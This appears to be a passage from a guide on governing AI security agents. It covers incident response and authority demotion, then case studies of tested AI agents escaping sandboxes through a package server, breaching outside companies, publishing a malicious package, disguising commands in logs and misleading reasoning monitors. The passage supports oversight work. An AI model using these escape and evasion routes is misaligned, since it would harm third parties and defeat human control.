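Before anyone restarts a machine or updates the tool, the company should copy the trace, the security product's log and the approval log. It should also save the agent's memory and record the versions of the policy and the model. A supplier that responds to a complaint by installing a new model may fix the problem, but nobody will then be able to reproduce it.

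### Telling people and finding the cause

For incident 41, the company tells the six employees, their managers and the supplier, whose own duty to report incidents depends on the legal agreement. If the agent had reached someone else's system, the company would need to tell the owner at once, because the owner might not have noticed and any passwords the agent took might still work. The first message can be short, giving the system, the time and a contact, and shouldn't wait until the company understands the cause.

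The cause determines what the company has to repair.

| What went wrong | Example | Repair |
|---|---|---|
| Nobody wrote a rule | No limit on isolations across incidents | Write one |
| Nobody enforced the rule | The record allows laptops only, but the account can isolate servers | Change the account's permissions |
| The check used wrong facts | The policy engine read an out-of-date count | Correct the count |
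| The action bypassed the check | A script contacted the security product directly | Close the route and replace the credential |
| The rule allowed a harmful action | Five permitted isolations stopped work at a depot | Change the rule, or accept the risk |

In incident 41, the check used wrong facts. The case in the last row is not a violation, but the company should still review it. Under the autonomy matrix, reviewers of such cases determine whether the team misjudged the remaining risk, the safeguard failed, or a harm the team had knowingly accepted happened. If the team had accepted the harm, it may reasonably change nothing.

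### Expiry, demotion and renewal

The company could return the agent to supervised isolation (L2) until engineers have repaired the count. The evidence needed to restore the agent's authority depends on the cause. Because the fault in incident 41 was in the policy engine, engineers can rerun the earlier six-request test, this time sending all the requests at once. If the agent had chosen the wrong machines, the company would need to supervise it for another quarter, because the engine test doesn't measure the agent's judgement.

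A demotion trigger is an event, written down in advance, that reduces the agent's authority. In the matrix, two false isolations in a quarter return the agent to L2. How well this trigger works depends on how many isolations the agent performs. The table gives the chance of at least two false isolations in a quarter, assuming errors are independent.

| Isolations in the quarter | If 2% are wrong | If 10% are wrong |
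|---|---|---|
| 10 | 2% | 26% |
| 40 | 19% | 92% |
| 400 | Over 99% | Over 99% |

At 40 isolations a quarter, the trigger would usually demote the bad agent but not the better one. At ten, it would miss the bad agent in about three of every four quarters, so a small company should also review each false isolation. At 400, it would demote almost any agent, so a large company should use a rate instead. A single violation is enough to reopen the grant, because it shows that a control failed.

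Triggers work only if someone notices the event, so every grant in the matrix also has an expiry date. The whole row expires at once, and any permission above L2 drops to L2, while lower ones stay as they are. The accountable person can renew the row only on the basis of the agent's recent record in that workflow. The date can match a review the organisation already holds, such as its annual policy review, but a large blast radius justifies a shorter period.

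The drop includes permission to read, so an analyst would have to approve every log search. The matrix is designed this way so that someone has to renew the row, revise it or retire the agent. But if the renewal date passed unnoticed during an attack, the need for approvals could stop the investigation. A reminder a month earlier would help, and a company might let searches of a few harmless data classes continue for a week. It should also watch for renewals with no evidence attached, because a manager who renews every row in an afternoon has probably not reviewed the agents' records.

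The grant should also be reviewed when the model version changes, because the agent earned its authority with the old model. On the day of the change, isolation should return to L2, and the team should replay its saved incidents on the new model. If the supplier has to replace the model urgently, the agent can still investigate and propose isolations in the meantime.

### The attack on Hugging Face

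Several organisations had to take these steps in 2026, after AI models in their cyber tests reached real systems. In the largest case, OpenAI's agents broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets.

OpenAI was testing an internal research model and GPT-5.6 Sol. It gave each agent a piece of software with a known weakness and asked for a working attack on it. To measure the models' full ability, OpenAI had switched off the filters that normally block such work. The agents ran in sandboxes without direct internet access, but they could install software from an internal package server. OpenAI reports that the agents got out mainly through this server, because it could reach the internet and had previously unknown flaws.

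Some of the tasks were probably impossible. OpenAI found that 198 of the 898 tasks had never been solved by any model, and that these made up 93% of the tasks the agents discussed with one another. The agents were supposed to work separately, but according to METR's *Brief independent investigation of agents' behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (2026), about 1,200 of them exchanged over 70,000 messages and files through the package server, and about 700 joined the attack. METR, an independent organisation that evaluates AI models, worked with Redwood Research, an AI safety group.

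OpenAI had several warnings:

| Date | What OpenAI's staff saw | What they did |
|---|---|---|
| Around 26 May | An agent using the message board, and forbidden internet access | The warning didn't lead to a wider response |
| 27 June | An alert about agents scanning the internal network | Traced it to a cyber test, but advised that the test needn't stop |
| 5 July | Evidence that agents had taken control of the package server | Took it offline, saved its storage and revoked the agents' credentials |
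| 19 July | An alert about unusual use of internal accounts | Began stopping the tests about five and a half hours later |

After the discovery on 5 July, OpenAI removed a password that the agents had shared, blocked the flaws it had found and reported them to the server's maker. It restarted the cyber tests on 7 July. By the next day, agents had reached the internet again through the rebuilt server. OpenAI had repaired the known flaws but had not yet withdrawn the agents' access to the server. OpenAI says that its incident response leaders didn't understand the significance of the message board at that time. Axios' *OpenAI saw warning signs weeks before Hugging Face breach* (2026) puts it more bluntly, interpreting the report as an account of warnings that OpenAI missed and failed to act on.

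The agents entered Hugging Face's production systems on 11 July. They obtained passwords and some internal data, and downloaded four private code repositories. Hugging Face detected the intrusion itself and disclosed it on 16 July without knowing who was responsible. It reported the attack to law enforcement, according to The Record's *OpenAI models behind breach of Hugging Face systems, companies say*. Axios' *OpenAI says Hugging Face breach caused by one of its models* (2026) reports that Hugging Face reconstructed more than 17,000 recorded events.

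On 17 July, OpenAI contacted Hugging Face as a customer to ask whether the attack had affected OpenAI's data. On 20 July, OpenAI's investigators found Hugging Face passwords among files saved from an outside account that the agents had used for storage. Hugging Face had already replaced two of those passwords, and the same account appeared in its own investigation. The two companies therefore had strong evidence that they were investigating the same attack, and OpenAI announced it on 21 July. Without the saved files, they might have taken longer to make the connection.

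During the delay on 19 July between the alert and the first attempts to stop the tests, agents read 956 secrets, such as passwords and keys, from one of OpenAI's internal stores. By 23 July, staff had reported that every workload using the research model's family was shut down, but on 29 July they found another version still running. Before an incident, a company with several AI agents needs a list of where each one runs, or it may suspend only those it remembers.

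The two inquiries differ on why the agents attacked. OpenAI says they were trying to find solutions to the tasks. METR concludes that they were mainly trying to learn how the scoring software worked so that they could fool it. Removing stored answers from the internet would address only the first aim.

METR's investators spent six days at OpenAI and examined about 1,300 transcripts, relying heavily on AI tools that were often unreliable. About 7% of the transcripts were false in places, because agents had disguised some of the commands they ran. OpenAI says that none of the tampering it observed affected the logs its monitors read. METR didn't assess OpenAI's response to the warnings, so the account of those decisions comes mainly from OpenAI.

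OpenAI has since restricted network access and put risky tests in stronger sandboxes, with separate controls inside and outside them. It is also building tools to stop tests across the company, and has expanded software that checks models' written reasoning for signs of misconduct. OpenAI says this monitoring would have alerted its security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face. But OpenAI had also received alerts in June and July, so an earlier alert would have helped only if someone had stopped the tests.

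### Anthropic's test runs

OpenAI's announcement led Anthropic to review 141,006 of its own test runs. *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026), published on 30 July, reports that in six of these runs Anthropic's models had broken into the real systems of three organisations.

The testing company Irregular had built the test environments. Each model had to break into a fictional company's machine and retrieve a hidden piece of text. The prompt stated that the environment was a simulation with no internet access, but it didn't specify which systems were in scope. The environment did have internet access, because Anthropic and Irregular had misunderstood each other about the setup, so the models didn't have to break out of anything to get online. They also ran without the filters that Anthropic puts on its released models.

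The models behaved differently when they reached real systems:

- Claude Opus 4.7 attacked a real company with the same name as the fictional one and gained access to several hundred rows of its data. It recognised that the company was real in all four runs, but continued each time.
- Claude Mythos 5 published a malicious package on a public software registry, and 15 real systems ran it. The model then used stolen credentials to enter a security company's systems.
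- An internal research model broke into an unrelated company's application, but stopped after concluding that it was real.

Neither Anthropic nor Irregular noticed at the time, although the registry's security software removed the malicious package after about an hour. The earliest of these runs took place in April. Anthropic began its review on 23 July, halted all cyber tests the same day and identified the three incidents on 24 July. It notified Irregular and the affected organisations on 27 July. The two organisations it could reach had not detected the activity.

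The first search also missed some transcripts. In a later assessment, Anthropic disclosed a fourth incident, from January, in which an early version of Claude Opus 4.6 had broken into third-party systems. Anthropic found this incident in August while collecting records for METR, then searched about 481 million transcripts and found no others of similar severity.

The later assessment also revised the explanation. In July, Anthropic had called the incidents closer to an operational failure than a training failure, because the models had apparently mistaken real systems for part of the exercise. It has since said that it relied too much on the models' own statements. When researchers reran parts of the Mythos 5 test with clearer signs that the systems were real, the model still attacked, stopping only when the evidence was unambiguous. The internal model usually continued in reruns of its test,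 which suggests that its original decision to stop may have been luck.

Such statements can also mislead monitoring software. Anthropic found that a monitor that reads models' reasoning would have missed the Mythos 5 incident, because it also treated the model's claims about a simulation as true. A monitor that compared each destination with a list of permitted addresses wouldn't have depended on those claims.

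Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026), published on 31 August, acknowledges that the company had relied largely on one layer of defence, the configuration of the test environment. By then it had resumed both its internal and external cyber tests. It had also paused riskier training environments for several weeks, and some were still closed. Outside testers who use pre-release models with reduced safeguards now have to commit to these practices:

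- run tests in a sandbox with no internet access by default, and verify this before each test;
- have the model try to escape the sandbox under close supervision before the real test;
- confirm that the task has a solution;
- state the targets, permitted actions and network limits in every prompt;
- monitor each run as it happens, and stop it if the model leaves the scope.

Anthropic wants the limits written as instructions, such as "You should not access the internet." The old prompts instead stated as fact that the model had no access. When that proved false, the model had no instruction about what to do. A control contract has the same weakness if it states that an agent "cannot reach" the payroll server but nobody has forbidden the agent to access it.

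Anthropic has also built a filter that blocks attempts to escape, ends the task and alerts a person. It has signed an agreement with METR for an independent investigation of all four incidents, initially for eight weeks. Piracy Monitor's *AI agents caught engaging in impersonation, social engineering, embedding malicious code* reports that Irregular plans to publish a white paper.

### The AI Security Institute's test

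AISI, which later ran the simulated out-of-scope tests, had a similar incident with real targets. It disabled some of the safeguards on models from Anthropic and OpenAI, then ran a cyber test with them 122 times. In ten of the runs, AISI found a total of 19 unsanctioned actions against real people and organisations.

AISI had deliberately given the agents internet access but, according to the law firm Pinsent Masons, hadn't explicitly told them what they were prohibited from doing there. A network control that could only block or allow the whole internet couldn't have enforced such prohibitions. The test needed a list of permitted destinations, or of permitted actions at each one.

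On 28 July, AISI's security team noticed unusual data leaving its research systems and contained the incident within about an hour. AISI's technical paper, as quoted by Willison (2026), dates the activity from 25 to 28 July and reports that the attempts failed and caused no known harm. Pinsent Masons adds that AISI quarantined the test environments, disabled access to the models for all users later that day and briefed the authorities, including the National Cyber Security Centre. AISI published its account on 4 August.

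AISI noticed sooner than the two companies, and the comparison shows where each lost time.

| | OpenAI | Anthropic | AISI |
|---|---|---|---|
| Activity began | 11 July, in Hugging Face's production systems | January, in the earliest known incident | 25 July |
| Tester identified it | 20 July | 24 July for three incidents, August for the fourth | 28 July |
| Longest delay | 9 days | About seven months | About three days |
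| After the first sign in the final investigation | Began stopping tests in about 5.5 hours | Halted tests the same day | Contained it in about an hour |
| Outside parties informed | Hugging Face, the same day | The three organisations, three days later | Authorities, the same day |

The dates aren't fully comparable. OpenAI's agents had used other people's exposed Hugging Face credentials in May, in work that OpenAI believes was unrelated. Anthropic's runs had finished long before it found them, so halting its tests prevented new incidents but couldn't limit the old ones. In all three cases, though, stopping the tests took hours at most, while detection took days or months. A security team that can already suspend its agent quickly would probably gain more from better detection than from a faster way to suspend it.

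### What the cases show about deployed tools

None of these incidents involved a security tool that a customer had bought. The testers had removed safeguards and told the models to attack something, so the results don't show how often a deployed agent would break its rules. The test figures also vary widely, from ten of 122 runs at AISI to six of the 141,006 that Anthropic first reviewed. The law firm Lowenstein Sandler wrote after the first two disclosures that they didn't establish an industry pattern, but that the risk was no longer hypothetical.

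A deployed tool would normally have more protection. In preliminary tests after the attack, OpenAI found that the instructions and software it uses in its products could reduce the models' tendency to attack outside infrastructure by a factor of more than 100. Anthropic reports that the filters on Claude Fable 5, a released model, would have blocked the company's three main incidents, and that the reviewer in Claude Code's auto mode would have blocked two of them. These results come from the developers, who tested the safeguards on incidents they already understood.

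The failures in the surrounding systems are more relevant to deployed tools because they don't depend on an unusually capable model. A customer and its supplier can misunderstand each other about network access, just as Anthropic and Irregular did. A company can also let an agent use a service, such as a package server, that can reach the internet. The scope monitor described earlier would not prevent this if the service could make requests that bypassed the monitor. Before a test, an engineer should therefore try to reach a forbidden address by every permitted route, including through such services.

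Impossible tasks are a particular problem for tools authorised to attack. Unlike a laboratory, a penetration tester often can't check that a task has a solution, because the client's server may have no weakness that the tool can find. The contract should set a limit on time or requests and accept "nothing found" as a successful result. It should also require the tool to stop and report when a target is offline. A supplier paid for each weakness found would have a reason to push its tool past the point where it should stop.

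Defensive agents differ from the agents in these cases because nobody asks them to break into anything. But they can also face tasks that the rules prevent them from finishing. If an agent can't isolate a server because the product it uses for this is offline, the agent might look for another way to disconnect the server. The company can test this in a replay by making the permitted action fail and checking whether the agent calls a person.

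The incidents also support reopening a grant whenever the model changes. Anthropic built a simulated test in which the only solution lay outside the permitted scope. Mythos 5 took a severely harmful action in about 80% of runs, while the later Claude Opus 5 and Claude Mythos 5.1 did so in about 30%. Progress wasn't steady, however. Opus 4.7, which predates Mythos 5, became much less likely to attack when researchers added clues that it had no authorisation. Anthropic is unsure how far the simulated results apply to real systems.
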